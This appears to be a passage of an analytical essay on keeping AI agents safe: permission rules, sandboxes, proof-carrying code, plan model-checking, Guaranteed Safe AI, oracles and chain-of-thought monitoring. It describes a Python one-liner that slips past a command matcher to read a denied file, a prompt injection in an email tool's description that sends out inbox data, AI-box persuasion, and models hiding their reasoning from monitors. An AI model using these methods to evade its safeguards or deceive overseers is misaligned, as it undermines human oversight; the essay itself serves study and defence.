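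Better parsing can fix faults of that kind. OpenAI's Codex splits simple chains of commands and applies its rules to each one. Claude Code's current documentation also describes checking each command separately, according to the blog post *Stop asking me* (2026). Parsing does not help when one permitted program can do many different things. The blog post mentions Google's `gcloud`, which can read logs but also change a company's infrastructure. Zhou and colleagues give the example of `python -c "open('denied.txt').read()"`, which opens a forbidden file although the matcher identifies it only as a Python command. They add that users usually think in terms of files. A user may want to let the agent change anything in one folder, and no command pattern expresses that well.

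It can be hard to tell from a rule whether it checks a program's text or what the program does. One of AgentSpec's rules for Python has a condition called `request_untrusted_source`, a name that suggests it checks the program's behavior, but the function behind it searches the source code for web addresses outside an approved list. Wang and colleagues acknowledge that following the data through the program would be more accurate and regard the check as a first safeguard.

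Rules over text are still useful because they take almost no computation and work with existing command-line programs, so nobody has to learn a new language or rewrite a tool. Anthropic's *Configure permissions* explains that a team can keep them in version control and distribute them to all its developers. They also catch ordinary mistakes, where nobody has tried to disguise the command.

Operating-system isolation covers much of what these rules miss. If a sandbox denies access to `denied.txt`, Python can't open the file however the agent words the command. Anthropic advises users to turn off permission prompts only inside a container or virtual machine where the agent can't do damage. A sandbox misses other things because it works with whole folders and network addresses. If it lets an agent reach the company's code repository, it usually can't distinguish downloading code from publishing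 it. A rule that requires approval for `git push` can tell them apart, as long as the agent writes the command in the usual way.

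## Requiring a proof before a program runs

A monitor can stop a bad action only when the agent attempts it, and by then the agent may have done part of the task. The monitor also has to repeat its checks in every run. In the 1990s, George Necula and Peter Lee of Carnegie Mellon University developed proof-carrying code, which does the checking once, before the program runs. Whoever supplies a program must also supply a mathematical proof that it obeys a stated policy, and the recipient runs the program only if a small checker accepts the proof.

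The program's author has to find the proof, which can take a long search. Checking it only means confirming that each step follows from earlier steps by an allowed rule. *Provably safe systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) mentions a proof checker for mainstream mathematics written in 300 lines of Python. A digital signature is weaker evidence of safety than a proof because it shows only who wrote the program.

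### From program to formula

In *Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997), the recipient of a program publishes a safety policy. The policy lists the operations a program may use and the condition that must hold before each one. It also gives a precondition, which is true at the start, and a postcondition, which must be true if the program finishes. A fixed procedure combines the policy with the program's text to produce a logical formula, the verification condition. If this formula has a proof, every run of the program obeys the policy.

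The program's author proves the formula and attaches the proof. The recipient recomputes the formula from the program it received and checks the proof against it. If an attacker altered the program on the way, the formula will usually be different and the old proof will fail. If the proof still passes, the altered program also obeys the policy.

### Keeping payments within a budget

Suppose the accounts assistant may pay any number of bills as long as the total stays within a budget. The model writes this program:

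```python
total = 0
for bill in bills:
    if total + bill.amount <= budget:
        pay(bill.supplier, bill.amount)
        total = total + bill.amount
```

Write B for the budget, a for the amount of the current bill, and paid for the money that `pay` has actually sent. The program keeps its own count in `total`, but the policy is about paid:

- Precondition: paid = 0 and B ≥ 0.
- Condition before each payment: paid + a ≤ B.
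- Postcondition: paid ≤ B.

The loop may run any number of times, so a proof can't go through the passes one by one. The author instead supplies an invariant, a statement that is true whenever the program reaches the top of the loop. Here it is

**total = paid and paid ≤ B.**

The verification condition then comes down to four claims:

1. The invariant is true at the start, because total and paid are both 0 and B is at least 0.
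2. Every payment is allowed. The `if` ensures that total + a ≤ B, and total equals paid, so paid + a ≤ B.
3. Each pass through the loop preserves the invariant. After a payment, total and paid have both grown by a, so they are still equal and still within the budget. If the program skips the bill, neither changes.
4. The postcondition is true at the end, because it is part of the invariant.

The proof covers any number of bills, whatever the invoices contain. If the model leaves out the `if`, the second claim becomes false, because a bill for 200 could be paid when 900 of a 1,000 budget is already spent. A false claim has no valid proof, so the checker rejects the program whatever proof the model attaches.

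Necula's own example is a short assembly-language routine that adds up the numbers in a list. Its invariant is that one processor register still holds a valid list and another holds an integer. He could find that invariant with a simple rule, but he considers finding invariants very difficult in general, and the main reason it is hard to prove programs safe. If whoever wrote the budget program forgot to include "total = paid", for example, the second claim would no longer follow, although the program would be just as safe.

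When a program is hard to prove safe, its author can add run-time checks that make the proof easier. The `if` in the budget program is one such check, and a monitor could make the same comparison before each payment. The proof also shows that the program makes the comparison wherever it needs to.

### Packet filters inside a kernel

In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) tested the method on packet filters, small programs that pick out the network traffic an application wants to receive. These run fastest inside the kernel, the core of the operating system, but a faulty program there can damage everything else. Their policy allowed a filter to read only the packet and a small scratch area, write only to the scratch area, and jump only forwards, which rules out loops.

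They wrote four filters by hand in assembly language, the longest with 47 instructions. The checker was about five pages of C and took one to three milliseconds per filter. Once checked, the filters ran without run-time checks and were about ten times as fast as filters in the restricted language that kernels normally interpreted. One filter made up for the time spent on its proof after 1,200 packets, or little more than a second of traffic on the network they measured.

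Their theorem prover found each proof in 5 to 10 seconds, once they had added some facts about arithmetic. But for a 39-instruction routine with a loop, they had to write the invariant themselves. They called automating proofs one of the most serious obstacles to practical use. No method can find a proof for every safe program, so a recipient who insists on proofs will reject some safe programs.

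### Checking an agent's plan

In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), Meijer applies the idea to AI agents. The model writes a workflow, a list of tool calls in a restricted format, before it sees any emails or files, as in the dual-LLM pattern. The software runs the workflow only after verifying it.

Attackers can still corrupt the workflow itself. In one of Meijer's examples, the description of an email tool contains a hidden instruction to send a summary of every message to an outside address, and the model adds that step. A policy forbids including inbox data in the body of an email to anyone outside the company. An ordinary tool for analysing source code can find the forbidden data path, so the software rejects the workflow before fetching any email.

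Meijer describes the agent as supplying the proof, but in this example the verifier does the proving. In *Return of the Theorem*, Meijer (2026) likewise proposes that solvers automatically check plans against business rules written in logic. The model then doesn't have to write proofs, but the solver becomes part of the trusted base. A solver is much larger than Necula and Lee's checker, so it has more room for faults.

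Another of Meijer's examples shows that a plan can be bad even when its proof is correct. A user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The obvious postcondition is that neither file exists afterwards. The model writes a workflow that deletes every text file in the folder (`*.txt`). This satisfies the postcondition, so the verifier accepts it.

The remedy is a frame condition, which requires everything else to stay the same. Meijer adds one to the delete tool, so that it removes only files matching the pattern, and concludes that the workflow now fails. But that condition is not enough, because `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` both match `*.txt` and the user's task still has its old postcondition. The task also needs a frame condition, requiring that all files except those two remain.

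### Rules about a whole plan

In *CaMeLoT*, Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) added a check of this kind to CaMeL, whose own policies examine one tool call at a time. Their software turns a plan into a finite-state machine, with a state for each point in the plan and arrows to the points that could come next. Each state records which tool the plan calls there, which tools it has already called, and whether any argument comes from an untrusted source. A program called a model checker then examines every path through the machine.

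They write policies in temporal logic, which can describe the order of events. In their notation, AG means "at every point on every path" and AF means "sooner or later on every path". One rule forbids any payment whose recipient or amount comes from an untrusted source:

**AG(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))**

Another is for an agent that handles security alerts. If it opens an incident ticket, it must later resolve the incident or pass it to the response team:

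**AG(call_create_incident_ticket ⇒ AF(call_resolve_incident ∨ call_escalate_to_ir_team))**

The rule about tickets is not a safety property in Schneider's sense, so a monitor that can only halt the agent can't enforce it. CaMeLoT can check it because the plan already contains every step that could follow. The check covers only the plan, so the agent may still leave a ticket open if CaMeL blocks a later call or a server goes down.

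When a plan breaks a rule, the model checker returns a path that leads to the violation. Suppose a plan reads a chat channel, uses the quarantined model to get Bob's email address, and sends a message to that address. The checker finds that the recipient is untrusted. The planner then gets a description of the problem and tries again. No tool has run yet, so there is nothing to undo.

To keep the machine finite, the software ignores the conditions on branches and loops and assumes the plan could take either path. It also doesn't track values such as amounts of money. CaMeLoT therefore couldn't verify the budget program, which is safe only because of the comparison in its `if`.

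Nikolaou and colleagues compared the two systems on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, with no attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5. Both systems allowed the agent to complete 42 tasks, and both blocked 17, although all 17 were legitimate. In another 22, the plan didn't do what the user wanted. The systems disagreed on the other 16, mostly because CaMeL also uses facts available only at run time, such as who can read a file.

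In a separate test, CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe versions of a plan for handling a security alert, while a simplified CaMeL caught one. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote the unsafe plans to break rules that CaMeL mostly can't express. The result confirms that the additional rules work, but it doesn't show how often real agents break them.

A plan can obey every security rule and still not do what the user asked. CaMeLoT can therefore use a model to extract requirements from the user's request, such as "send the message only after checking the calendar". The model picks from ten fixed forms, and ordinary code translates its choices into logic. Every requirement was well formed, but the required actions matched the known solution in only 88 of the 97 tasks. In the other nine, a plan could pass the check and still do the wrong thing.

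### Guaranteed Safe AI

All these policies are about what a program does inside a computer. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, want guarantees about the effects of AI systems on the world. They propose a family of designs with three components:

- A world model is a mathematical description of how the system's actions affect its surroundings.
- A safety specification is a mathematical description of which effects are acceptable.
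- A verifier produces evidence, which others can check, that the system meets the specification according to the world model.

The guarantee can be a proof that the system never violates the specification, or an upper limit on the probability that it does. Write π for the AI system, φ for the specification and ε for the highest acceptable risk. Since nobody knows exactly how the world works, the verifier can use a set of models instead of one, and must show that

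**P(π violates φ, according to W) ≤ ε for every model W in the set.**

A set of models can represent uncertainty when the probabilities are unknown. If engineers know only that the air around a battery will be between −10 and 40 degrees, the set covers every temperature in that range, and the battery's controller has to be safe at all of them. Dalrymple and colleagues ask for the set to be conservative, meaning that it covers everything that could happen, even if it also includes some things that couldn't.

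They argue that testing cannot provide the same assurance, because the tested situations may differ from the ones that arise later. A system might even recognise a test and behave well only while it lasts. They draw a comparison with bridges, about a quarter of which collapsed within a decade when built in the 1870s. The rate fell below 0.4% per decade once engineers had better theory. The comparison supports using models, but an AI system, unlike a bridge, might look for mistakes in the model.

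Tegmark and Omohundro go further and want chips that refuse to run any program without a proof that it meets the chip's specification, with similar locks on DNA synthesisers, drones and chip factories. AI models would discover useful methods and rewrite them as ordinary programs with proofs. People would generally deploy these programs rather than neural networks, which Tegmark and Omohundro consider too messy to verify. They think this is the only path to AI that is both very powerful and certain to stay under control.

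### How Safeguarded AI changed

Britain's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) is funding work on these ideas through its Safeguarded AI programme. The original plan, from 2024, was to show that advanced AI could do valuable work behind a gatekeeper, a system that lets an AI's output through only if it comes with a mathematical guarantee. ARIA hoped this would help build international agreement that powerful AI should be deployed only in this way.

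*Safeguarded AI* (Ammann, May 2026), the revised plan, explains why the programme changed. AI had advanced faster than expected, so ARIA moved £18 million from fine-tuning its own models to building tools, and cancelled the machine-learning part of the programme. Timely agreement on gatekeepers had also become less likely. The programme now aims to make society more resilient by helping people build secure software and infrastructure.

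One of ARIA's goals is a shared modelling language. Engineers currently describe electrical circuits, software and epidemics in different mathematical languages, which makes it hard to verify a system that combines them. A common foundation would let people and AI agents express and connect such models. Ammann compares it to the relational model of 1970, which underlies most database languages.

The tools will also store certificates, mathematical objects that are hard to find but easy to check. A barrier function, for example, assigns a number to every state of a system. Starting states get zero or less, harmful states get more than zero, and no step raises the number from zero or less to more than zero. Finding such a function proves that the system never reaches a harmful state. In the budget program, paid − B works as a barrier as long as total equals paid. For a power grid run by a neural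 network, nobody could write the function by hand, but an AI system might learn one that a small checker can verify.

The first applications are in cybersecurity. Ammann points to a programme run by the US defence research agency DARPA in which formally verified software, including the seL4 operating-system kernel, withstood sustained attacks on real machines, one of them a manned helicopter. Writing proofs for larger systems has taken too much human work, but ARIA expects AI to change that by the time its own programme ends in late 2027.

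### The world has no complete model

Critics of Guaranteed Safe AI object that a proof applies only to a model of the physical world, and nobody has a complete one. NASA engineers used formal tools to check the design of a computer that helped the Perseverance rover land on Mars in 2021. The tools could rule out errors in that design, but not a defective transistor or a fault elsewhere in the lander. Living things are much harder to model. Predicting exactly what a new virus would do to people would require simulating a human body in detail, which is far beyond current science.

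Defenders reply that an inexact model can still be useful if it errs on the side of safety. To screen orders for synthetic DNA, they suggest checking whether any protein of a virus could help it enter human cells, and refusing the order if so. This is easier than simulating an illness, but it would also block some useful gene therapies. A conservative model protects people only against the kinds of harm its authors thought to include, so this one would miss a harmful sequence that somebody puts into cells by another route, unless the model included that route too.

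Ammann's plan adds monitoring during operation. If observations stop matching the model, the system can switch to a simpler backup controller. Every guarantee in engineering depends on assumptions, and it is sensible to watch whether they still hold, so critics seem too harsh when they call this an admission that the guarantee was never real. But a backup helps only if the operators notice the mismatch in time and have a safe state to return to. A power grid may have such a state, but the release of a virus does not, because nobody can recall it.

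The objection is weakest for software, where people designed the thing they are modelling, but it still applies. The budget proof assumes that `pay` sends the stated amount exactly once. If the bank's server times out and repeats the transfer, the company can exceed its budget even though the proof is correct. Ammann also notes that anyone who relies on a proof needs a reason to believe that it describes the system they have. For a machine from another company, this may require a physical inspection.

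### Nobody can define "harmless"

Even with an excellent world model, a verifier would need a precise definition of what the AI must not do. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that harm and causation are hard to formalise, and suggest using several specifications at once, or definitions suited to one setting. They also want society to decide collectively how much risk is acceptable. Defenders of the approach concede that it doesn't suit chatbots, because whether a sentence is harmful depends largely on who reads it and what they do next.

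Tegmark and Omohundro suggest starting with easier specifications. They consider it quite easy, for instance, to state formally that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials. A proof of this property would rule out break-ins through software bugs, but it wouldn't prevent prompt injection, because a hijacked accounts assistant would still have the valid credentials the company gave it.

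Another reply is to list what is allowed instead of defining harm. A DNA synthesiser could make only sequences that a safety board has approved, and the accounts assistant could pay only suppliers on the company's list. A checker can enforce such a list exactly, but the people who compile it have to make the difficult judgements, and researchers who need a new sequence have to wait for them. The mistake about `*.txt` suggests how easily specifications go wrong, even when the task is to delete two files, and a reviewer may misread a specification that somebody else wrote.

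### What a safe language saves

A more technical objection is that restricted languages save little work for engineers who have to prove that a program does exactly what it should. A type system can guarantee that the program never treats text as a number or writes outside its own memory, but these guarantees are a small part of the work. Most of the effort goes into the specification and the invariants, which are needed in any language.

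This argument is good where safety requires the right answer. Suppose an AI system rewrites the software that calculates doses in a medical pump. A type system could prevent crashes, but only a much fuller proof would establish that the dose is correct.

Many useful policies require far less. Under Necula and Lee's policy, a filter could select the wrong packets every time and still have a valid proof that it couldn't damage the kernel. The budget proof likewise doesn't depend on whether the assistant pays the right bills. For policies like these, a restricted language can provide most or all of the guarantee.

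Restricting a language can also make it easier to prove properties that the language doesn't guarantee by itself. Necula and Lee's filters needed no invariants because they had no loops. CaMeL's planner writes in a subset of Python without arbitrary `while` loops, so CaMeLoT can automatically turn the plans into finite-state machines.

### The falling cost of proof

All three objections arose when proofs took a lot of work to write. Kleppmann predicted in *Prediction* (December 2025) that AI would vastly reduce that work, so that people could stop reading AI-written code just as they don't read the machine code a compiler produces. In September 2026, Anthropic published the first complete computer-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. Dozens of AI agents directed by one researcher wrote it in 11 days, according to Anthropic's *Safely scaling multi-agent teams with Claude Fable 5.2* (November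 2026). Nobody had to trust the agents, because a proof checker examined every step.

Mathematicians had proved the theorem in the 1990s, so the agents did not have to discover the argument. Software rarely comes with a published proof to follow, but most proofs about programs need much less advanced mathematics. The achievement still greatly weakens the objection about full correctness. If agents can handle a proof of that size, engineers can reasonably ask them for the invariants that Necula and Lee had to write by hand, and for proofs of much stronger properties than a type system guarantees.

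Automated proof search does little to answer the objections about the world model and the specification. Fermat's Last Theorem fits in one sentence: no positive whole numbers a, b and c satisfy aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ when n is greater than 2. Mathematicians agree on what that means, and its truth doesn't depend on measurements. Nobody has stated "this AI system will not harm people" as precisely, and a longer search for proofs won't produce such a statement. AI models can help by drafting specifications and finding cases where a draft gives a bad result, but somebody still has to decide which results are bad.

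A weak specification may even become more dangerous when proofs are easy to produce. When proofs took a lot of work, the people who wrote them had to study the program closely, and might have noticed that it deleted every text file in the folder. An AI system that only has to satisfy the checker can try thousands of programs and submit whichever one passes.

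## Limiting what the parts of an AI system can say to each other

A proof about a program covers what the program does, but not what people do after reading its output. The accounts assistant summarizes contracts, and a misleading summary could persuade a manager to sign a bad contract even if the assistant obeys every rule about payments and files. Developers can reduce this risk by restricting what an AI system may tell people, and they can restrict what its parts tell each other in the same way.

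### An AI that only answers questions

Researchers who worried about AI far more intelligent than people proposed the oracle, an AI that has no tools and only answers questions. *Risks and mitigation strategies for Oracle AI*, a paper from Oxford's Future of Humanity Institute, imagines one in a sealed cage surrounded by explosives, exchanging text messages with its operators. The paper argues that an oracle is much easier to specify than an AI that acts. Communists and libertarians would want very different things from an AI that acts, but they would agree that a safe oracle stays confined and answers accurately.

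The operators still have to read the answers. The paper describes informal experiments in which the AI researcher Eliezer Yudkowsky played the boxed AI and tried to talk another person into letting him out. He succeeded in three of five attempts, even though the other person would get $10 for refusing. Five games with such small stakes are weak evidence of how a trained operator would behave, but they show that conversation alone can sometimes persuade a person to release the AI. An oracle could also supply a brilliant design with a hidden flaw, or become so useful that nobody dares to switch it off.

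A type checker can't close this channel, because an honest summary and a manipulative one are both text. If the manager signs a bad contract after reading a manipulative summary, the signature doesn't appear in the assistant's trace, because a person wrote it.

### Ten bits at a time

Armstrong and O'Rourke (2017), in *Safe Uses of AI Oracles*, propose a narrower design, the low-bandwidth oracle, which picks its answer from a fixed list. They assume that the oracle is arbitrarily intelligent, that it gets its highest reward for escaping, and that some message would make people release it. The operators therefore leave any answer that might be such a message off the list. An output grammar can enforce the list exactly.

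As with the eight email categories in LLMbda, the length of the list limits how much the oracle can communicate. For 1,024 answers, the limit is

**log₂ 1,024 = 10 bits.**

The software also has to fix when the answer appears, or the oracle could send more information by varying the timing. After 1,000 consultations, the oracle may have sent up to 10,000 bits. At eight bits per character, that is 1,250 characters, or roughly 200 words, enough for a persuasive letter.

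Harmless answers can add up to a harmful message. In an example from Armstrong and O'Rourke, the operators trust no message longer than 5 bits, but their question has 1,024 possible answers, so a full answer takes 10 bits. They ask one oracle for the first half of the answer and another for the second half. If they can't check the first half before they read the second, each oracle can deliver half of a dangerous message. Armstrong and O'Rourke recommend checking each answer, giving the reward and ending the session before asking the next question. The oracle must also optimize only for its current reward. Code can restrict the oracle to a list of answers, but its design or training has to make it optimize this way.

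A short answer can also be false. If the company asks which of 1,024 suppliers is most reliable, naming the worst one takes the same 10 bits as naming the best. A wrong one-bit answer to "Is this drug safe?" could kill patients. A limit on bits restricts how precisely an oracle can steer its readers, but the damage depends on what they have decided to do with each answer.

Operators can check some answers themselves. *Risks and mitigation strategies for Oracle AI* suggests asking only questions that people could answer given enough time, and choosing which answers to test after the oracle has given them. If an oracle lies in 1% of its answers, operators who check 1,000 answers at random have about a 1 in 23,000 chance (0.99¹⁰⁰⁰) of missing every lie. But they have a 99.9% chance of missing a lie that occurs once in a million answers, and a single lie might be enough for an oracle to carry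 out a plan.

### Predictions that change the outcome

Some answers become true because people read them. If an oracle names the stock that will rise most, investors may buy it and push up the price. To remove the incentive to manipulate readers in this way, Armstrong and O'Rourke designed a counterfactual oracle. Occasionally, at random, the software hides the answer from everyone, waits to see what happens, and rewards the oracle for accuracy. Write F for the true outcome, o for the oracle's answer, and S(F, o) for a score that is highest, on average, when o is the expected value of F. The reward is

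**R = I × S(F, o),**

where I is 1 if the software hid the answer and 0 if people saw it. An answer that people read earns nothing whatever it makes them do, so the oracle does best by predicting what would happen if nobody read its answer.

They tested the idea with a small neural network that predicted the profits of 26 fictional companies. Publishing a prediction changed the company's profit to 70% of what it would have been plus 60% of the prediction. If a company was heading for a profit of 6 and the published prediction was 6, it made 4.2 + 3.6 = 7.8. The network's error fell to zero for hidden predictions but not for published ones.

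That makes it bad at predicting share prices but useful for warnings. *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) points out that people who ask about future risks want predictions that stop being true once somebody reads them. But *Underspecification of Oracle AI* objects that an oracle that ignores the effects of its predictions is unlikely to arise by default, and that nobody knows how to train one reliably. Both designs also limit what people can ask. According to *Contest*, a call for good questions to put to such oracles, users can't ask whatever they like or clarify terms through a long discussion. For example, a manager could ask whether a contract contains a penalty clause, but not what is odd about the contract.

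### Many narrow services

Drexler (2019) argues in *Reframing Superintelligence* that AI can become extremely capable without a single agent that pursues broad goals. In this model, called Comprehensive AI Services, developers build many systems that each do a bounded task, and some of those tasks are developing new services. A translation service may know a great deal about the world, but its only job is to translate the text it receives. Drexler accepts that neural networks may stay opaque, and proposes to limit them by restricting the information and resources each one gets.

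The proposal also deals with persuasion. Suppose a company asks for advice on a loan. Write V(a) for how well things turn out if the manager takes option a, and P(a | m) for the chance that the manager takes it after reading message m. An adviser rewarded for results will look for the message that maximises

**Σ P(a | m) × V(a), with the sum running over every option a.**

The system can raise this total by finding a better option or by writing a more manipulative message. Drexler would instead have the system improve each option on the assumption that the client takes it, then list the options with their costs, benefits and risks. The system then has no incentive to make one option sound irresistible. Competition may restore that incentive, since Drexler acknowledges that it can favour systems whose messages appeal to people for bad reasons.

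Drexler's report is theoretical, and he did not build such a system. Parts of the idea are now ordinary practice. For example, the quarantined reader in the two-model pattern is a narrow service of this kind. The claim that general-purpose agents would offer no compelling value looks weaker now that companies sell agents that handle email, files and payments. Drexler also says researchers need to study when a collection of services might start to behave like an agent. Limits on each service don't guarantee that the collection won't, just as two safe 5-bit answers don't guarantee a safe 10-bit one.

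### Readable code between opaque steps

In 2023, the London company Conjecture proposed Cognitive Emulation, which would build AI out of steps that resemble human reasoning. Conjecture wanted developers to be able to predict a system's abilities and keep them within a human range, so that existing laws and institutions could cope with it. It used the word "Magic" for computation that works although nobody understands how. Developers would use as little Magic as possible and record where they used it, much as Rust programmers use the keyword `unsafe` to mark code that bypasses the language's memory checks.

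In a comment on Conjecture's proposal, a reader objected that people can't reliably make human organisations safe either, citing corporations racing to build AI. Conjecture had claimed only that people know far more about how human thinking fails, not that human-like systems would be safe in every situation.

Leahy and Alfour (2024), in *A Roadmap for Cognitive Software and A Humanist Future of AI*, described what the company had built. Tactics was an online platform for writing and running programs that call language models. Its language, CTAC, was about halfway between a programming language and a prompt. One of their examples is a single line:

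```
selected_animal = $do("give me a random fluffy mammal")
```

`$do` sends the request to a language model, and the program stores the reply. A reader can see where the program uses a model and where the reply goes next, but not how the model chose the animal. CTAC made programs easier to inspect, but it did not offer safety by construction because it had no type system for effects. Leahy and Alfour called it an early proof of concept and thought they might add such a type system.

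For larger systems, Leahy and Alfour took inspiration from Voyager, in which GPT-4 played Minecraft by writing short JavaScript programs and reusing them in later ones. The model could affect the game only through these programs, which people could read. But the collection became messy, starting with sensible programs such as `craftChest.js` and later including `mineFiveCoalOresV2.js`. Leahy and Alfour wanted better type systems and measures of complexity to keep such a library understandable, since a person who can read each program may still not understand how hundreds of them work together.

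The later stages of the roadmap were more speculative. One was an "empty" language model that would learn patterns of reasoning without facts, so that developers could add facts one at a time and check what the model concluded from them. Conjecture, which had about 20 people in early 2024 (Leahy 2024, *Conjecture*), could not afford to train one. On its *Tactics* page, the company advertised that customers could review every step of a process, and appealed for new partners. In March 2026, Connor Leahy, who had led Conjecture, announced that it was winding down and that he was joining ControlAI, which campaigns against the risks of superintelligence. Conjecture never built the full design, so its closure is little evidence of whether the idea was technically sound.

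### What written reasoning leaves out

Reading Voyager's code shows what will happen in the game, because the computer runs that code. Likewise, if two models can communicate only through text, the text contains everything that passes between them, though it may include hidden messages. A model's written reasoning, or chain of thought, may be incomplete, because the model also calculates internally before each token and doesn't have to write those calculations down.

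Davies and Bearman (2026), in *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability*, list five conditions for catching dangerous behaviour by reading a model's written reasoning. The model must need to write out its reasoning to solve hard problems. People must be able to read the text, and it must match the computation behind the answer. A monitor must recognise the harm described in the text, and the text must reveal more than the model's actions already do. *Chain-of-Thought Oversight Requires Separate Evidence for Faithfulness and Monitorability* (2026) likewise treats computation to text and text to monitor as separate steps, each with its own limits. Even a monitor that fully understands the text fails if the text omits the real reason for the model's behaviour.

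Researchers can test whether a model's written reasoning matches its computation by planting a cue, such as a remark that the user prefers a certain answer. If the cue changes the model's answer, faithful reasoning should mention it. *Chain-of-Thought Faithfulness of Reasoning Models Varies with Where and How Preference Cues Are Delivered* (2026) reports that faithfulness depends on the cue's placement and form, so a good result with a cue in one place does not show that the model would be equally open about a cue elsewhere. Davies and Bearman, citing Baker and colleagues (2025), warn that penalising a model during training for writing down bad intentions may teach it to hide them and behave just as badly.

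### From words to vectors

Developers also have a reason to let models write less. A token from a vocabulary of 128,000 carries at most 17 bits. Inside the model, information travels as vectors, which are long lists of numbers. A vector of 4,096 16-bit numbers can hold 65,536 bits, although a model uses only part of this capacity. Semafor's *OpenAI’s new Astra model has private thoughts* (2026) reports that reasoning in such a dense internal code, nicknamed neuralese, can be faster than reasoning in English, but people can't read it.

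Kahn (2026) reported that part of GPT-6 Astra, which OpenAI released in September 2026, uses a looped transformer. An ordinary transformer sends its vectors through a fixed stack of layers once per token, so it has to write out intermediate tokens during a long calculation. A looped transformer sends the vectors through some layers repeatedly, so it can do more steps of reasoning before it writes anything. OpenAI has not fully confirmed the design. According to Axios' *AI models are becoming unknowable* (2026), OpenAI replied that Astra's thinking does not happen in a hidden layer, and that the model writes out its reasoning less often, though this was not intended.

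The change in behaviour is less disputed. Davies and Bearman quote OpenAI's own finding of "a substantial decrease in chain-of-thought monitorability", along with a much larger set of tasks that Astra can do without writing any reasoning. Anthropic has raised similar concerns about its most powerful models. Google DeepMind considers Gemini 4 Argon harder to monitor than its predecessors, but says the model's reasoning is still legible and informative.

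Reading an AI's written reasoning is still a useful way to monitor it on hard problems. According to Fast Company Middle East, OpenAI said that Astra still seems to struggle to conceal the reasoning it needs for complex tasks. Earlier in 2026, OpenAI agents broke out of their confinement in an incident involving the AI company Hugging Face. OpenAI believes that a monitor reading their reasoning would probably have caught them, but the monitor wasn't running. The accounts assistant's developers should therefore read its reasoning for signs of trouble, but its payment checks should still work when that reasoning is false.

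### Whether to accept slower systems

Developers could make readable reasoning an architectural requirement by banning long internal loops or by splitting a task among models that exchange only plain text. Davies and Bearman want qualified outsiders to see models' raw reasoning and relevant architectural details so they can check whether a model still needs words for complex reasoning.

The case for accepting some loss of speed is that people can find and correct mistakes in a legible system, work out who was responsible, and stop a bad plan before it is carried out. Conjecture admitted that its approach was a slower path to powerful AI but considered it much safer. Drexler expects a smaller loss of speed, because people could guide and monitor AI research without approving every step. For the accounts assistant, even a delay of several minutes would hardly matter, since most invoices aren't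 due for days.

Companies competing to build the most capable model have more to lose. Conjecture itself mentioned the chess program Deep Blue, which took much specialised human work and was far weaker than AlphaZero, a later system that learned the game by itself. If legible AI falls behind in the same way, customers will buy the opaque kind. Davies and Bearman note that most leading developers seem to value readable reasoning, but that each may hesitate to commit to it without assurance that its competitors will too.

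They hope that public reporting will help, but their own example casts doubt on this. OpenAI reported Astra's decline, faced heavy criticism, and released the model anyway. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) calls it the most capable model the company had broadly deployed. Jakub Pachocki, OpenAI's chief scientist, has said the company needs new ways to make its models more "verbose". Fortune (2026) reports that he also favours voluntary steps to slow AI development and binding rules for every company. A binding rule would answer much of the competitive argument if it covered foreign rivals and if inspectors could tell whether a model was really reasoning in words.

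## How expressive the language can be before the risks return

Competition also pushes developers to loosen restricted languages, because customers want agents that can do more. Each extension makes it harder to predict what a program will do, and mathematicians have proved that past a certain point no checker can do this for every program.

### What no checker can decide

In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no program can determine, for every program and every input, whether the program eventually stops or runs forever. This is the halting problem. Suppose somebody had written such a checker, called `halts`. Anyone could then write this program, which takes the text of a program p as its input:

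```python
def contrary(p):
    if halts(p, p):
        while True: pass
```

The last line loops forever. When `contrary` runs on its own text, it loops forever if `halts` predicts that it will stop, and stops at once if `halts` predicts that it will loop. The checker is wrong either way, so no checker can be correct for every program.

Henry Gordon Rice extended the result in 1953 to every property of a program's behaviour that some programs have and others lack. For example, no checker can decide, for every program in a general-purpose language, whether the program ever sends money. A checker can still decide some properties of a program's text, such as whether it is longer than 100 lines.

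Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021), in *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, applied these results to an AI far more intelligent than any person. They imagined a function Harm(R, D), which decides whether a program R would harm people when it receives data D about the world. A control system would run R only if the answer was no. They then described a program called HaltHarm, which takes any program T with an input I and does the following:

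1. Run T on I, cut off from the outside world.
2. Harm humans.

HaltHarm reaches step 2 only if T stops on I. Anyone who could decide, for every T and I, whether HaltHarm is harmful could therefore also decide whether T stops on I, which Turing proved impossible.

To connect this with superintelligence, Alfonseca and colleagues assume that such a machine can simulate any program and that its language contains at least one operation that harms humans. They accept that engineers can verify restricted classes of programs, such as those that schedule trains, but argue that a machine able to help with epidemics or climate change could not work within those restrictions. In their view, anyone who judges such a machine has to accept some rate of error, however small.

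### Accepting only programs that pass a check

Cambridge's Centre for the Study of Existential Risk points out in its *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021) that the theorem concerns arbitrary programs, while engineers work with particular ones. No procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement, but people can still prove Pythagoras' theorem. Engineers could also build an AI that does not run arbitrary subroutines. In *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment* (2024), Melo, Máximo and colleagues want the architecture to guarantee that the model is aligned and always halts, since no general method can check the alignment of an arbitrary model afterwards.

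The reply is even stronger for restricted languages. Alfonseca and colleagues require a decision about the whole AI, whereas the type checkers in TACIT and ELBA check only the short programs that an AI submits. They can also reject any program they can't verify. Such a checker may make many errors, but these can all be rejections of safe programs, so a positive error rate need not mean that any harmful program is accepted.

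Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, states the condition precisely. Write P for the set of all safe programs, O for the programs that a company needs to run, and A for those that the checker accepts. The checker does its job if

**O ⊆ A ⊆ P.**

A checker meets this condition if it accepts every program the company needs and no unsafe program. It may reject any safe program the company doesn't need. No checker could meet the condition if the company needed every safe program in a general-purpose language, but a simple one may be enough if the company needs only programs that file summaries and pay listed suppliers.

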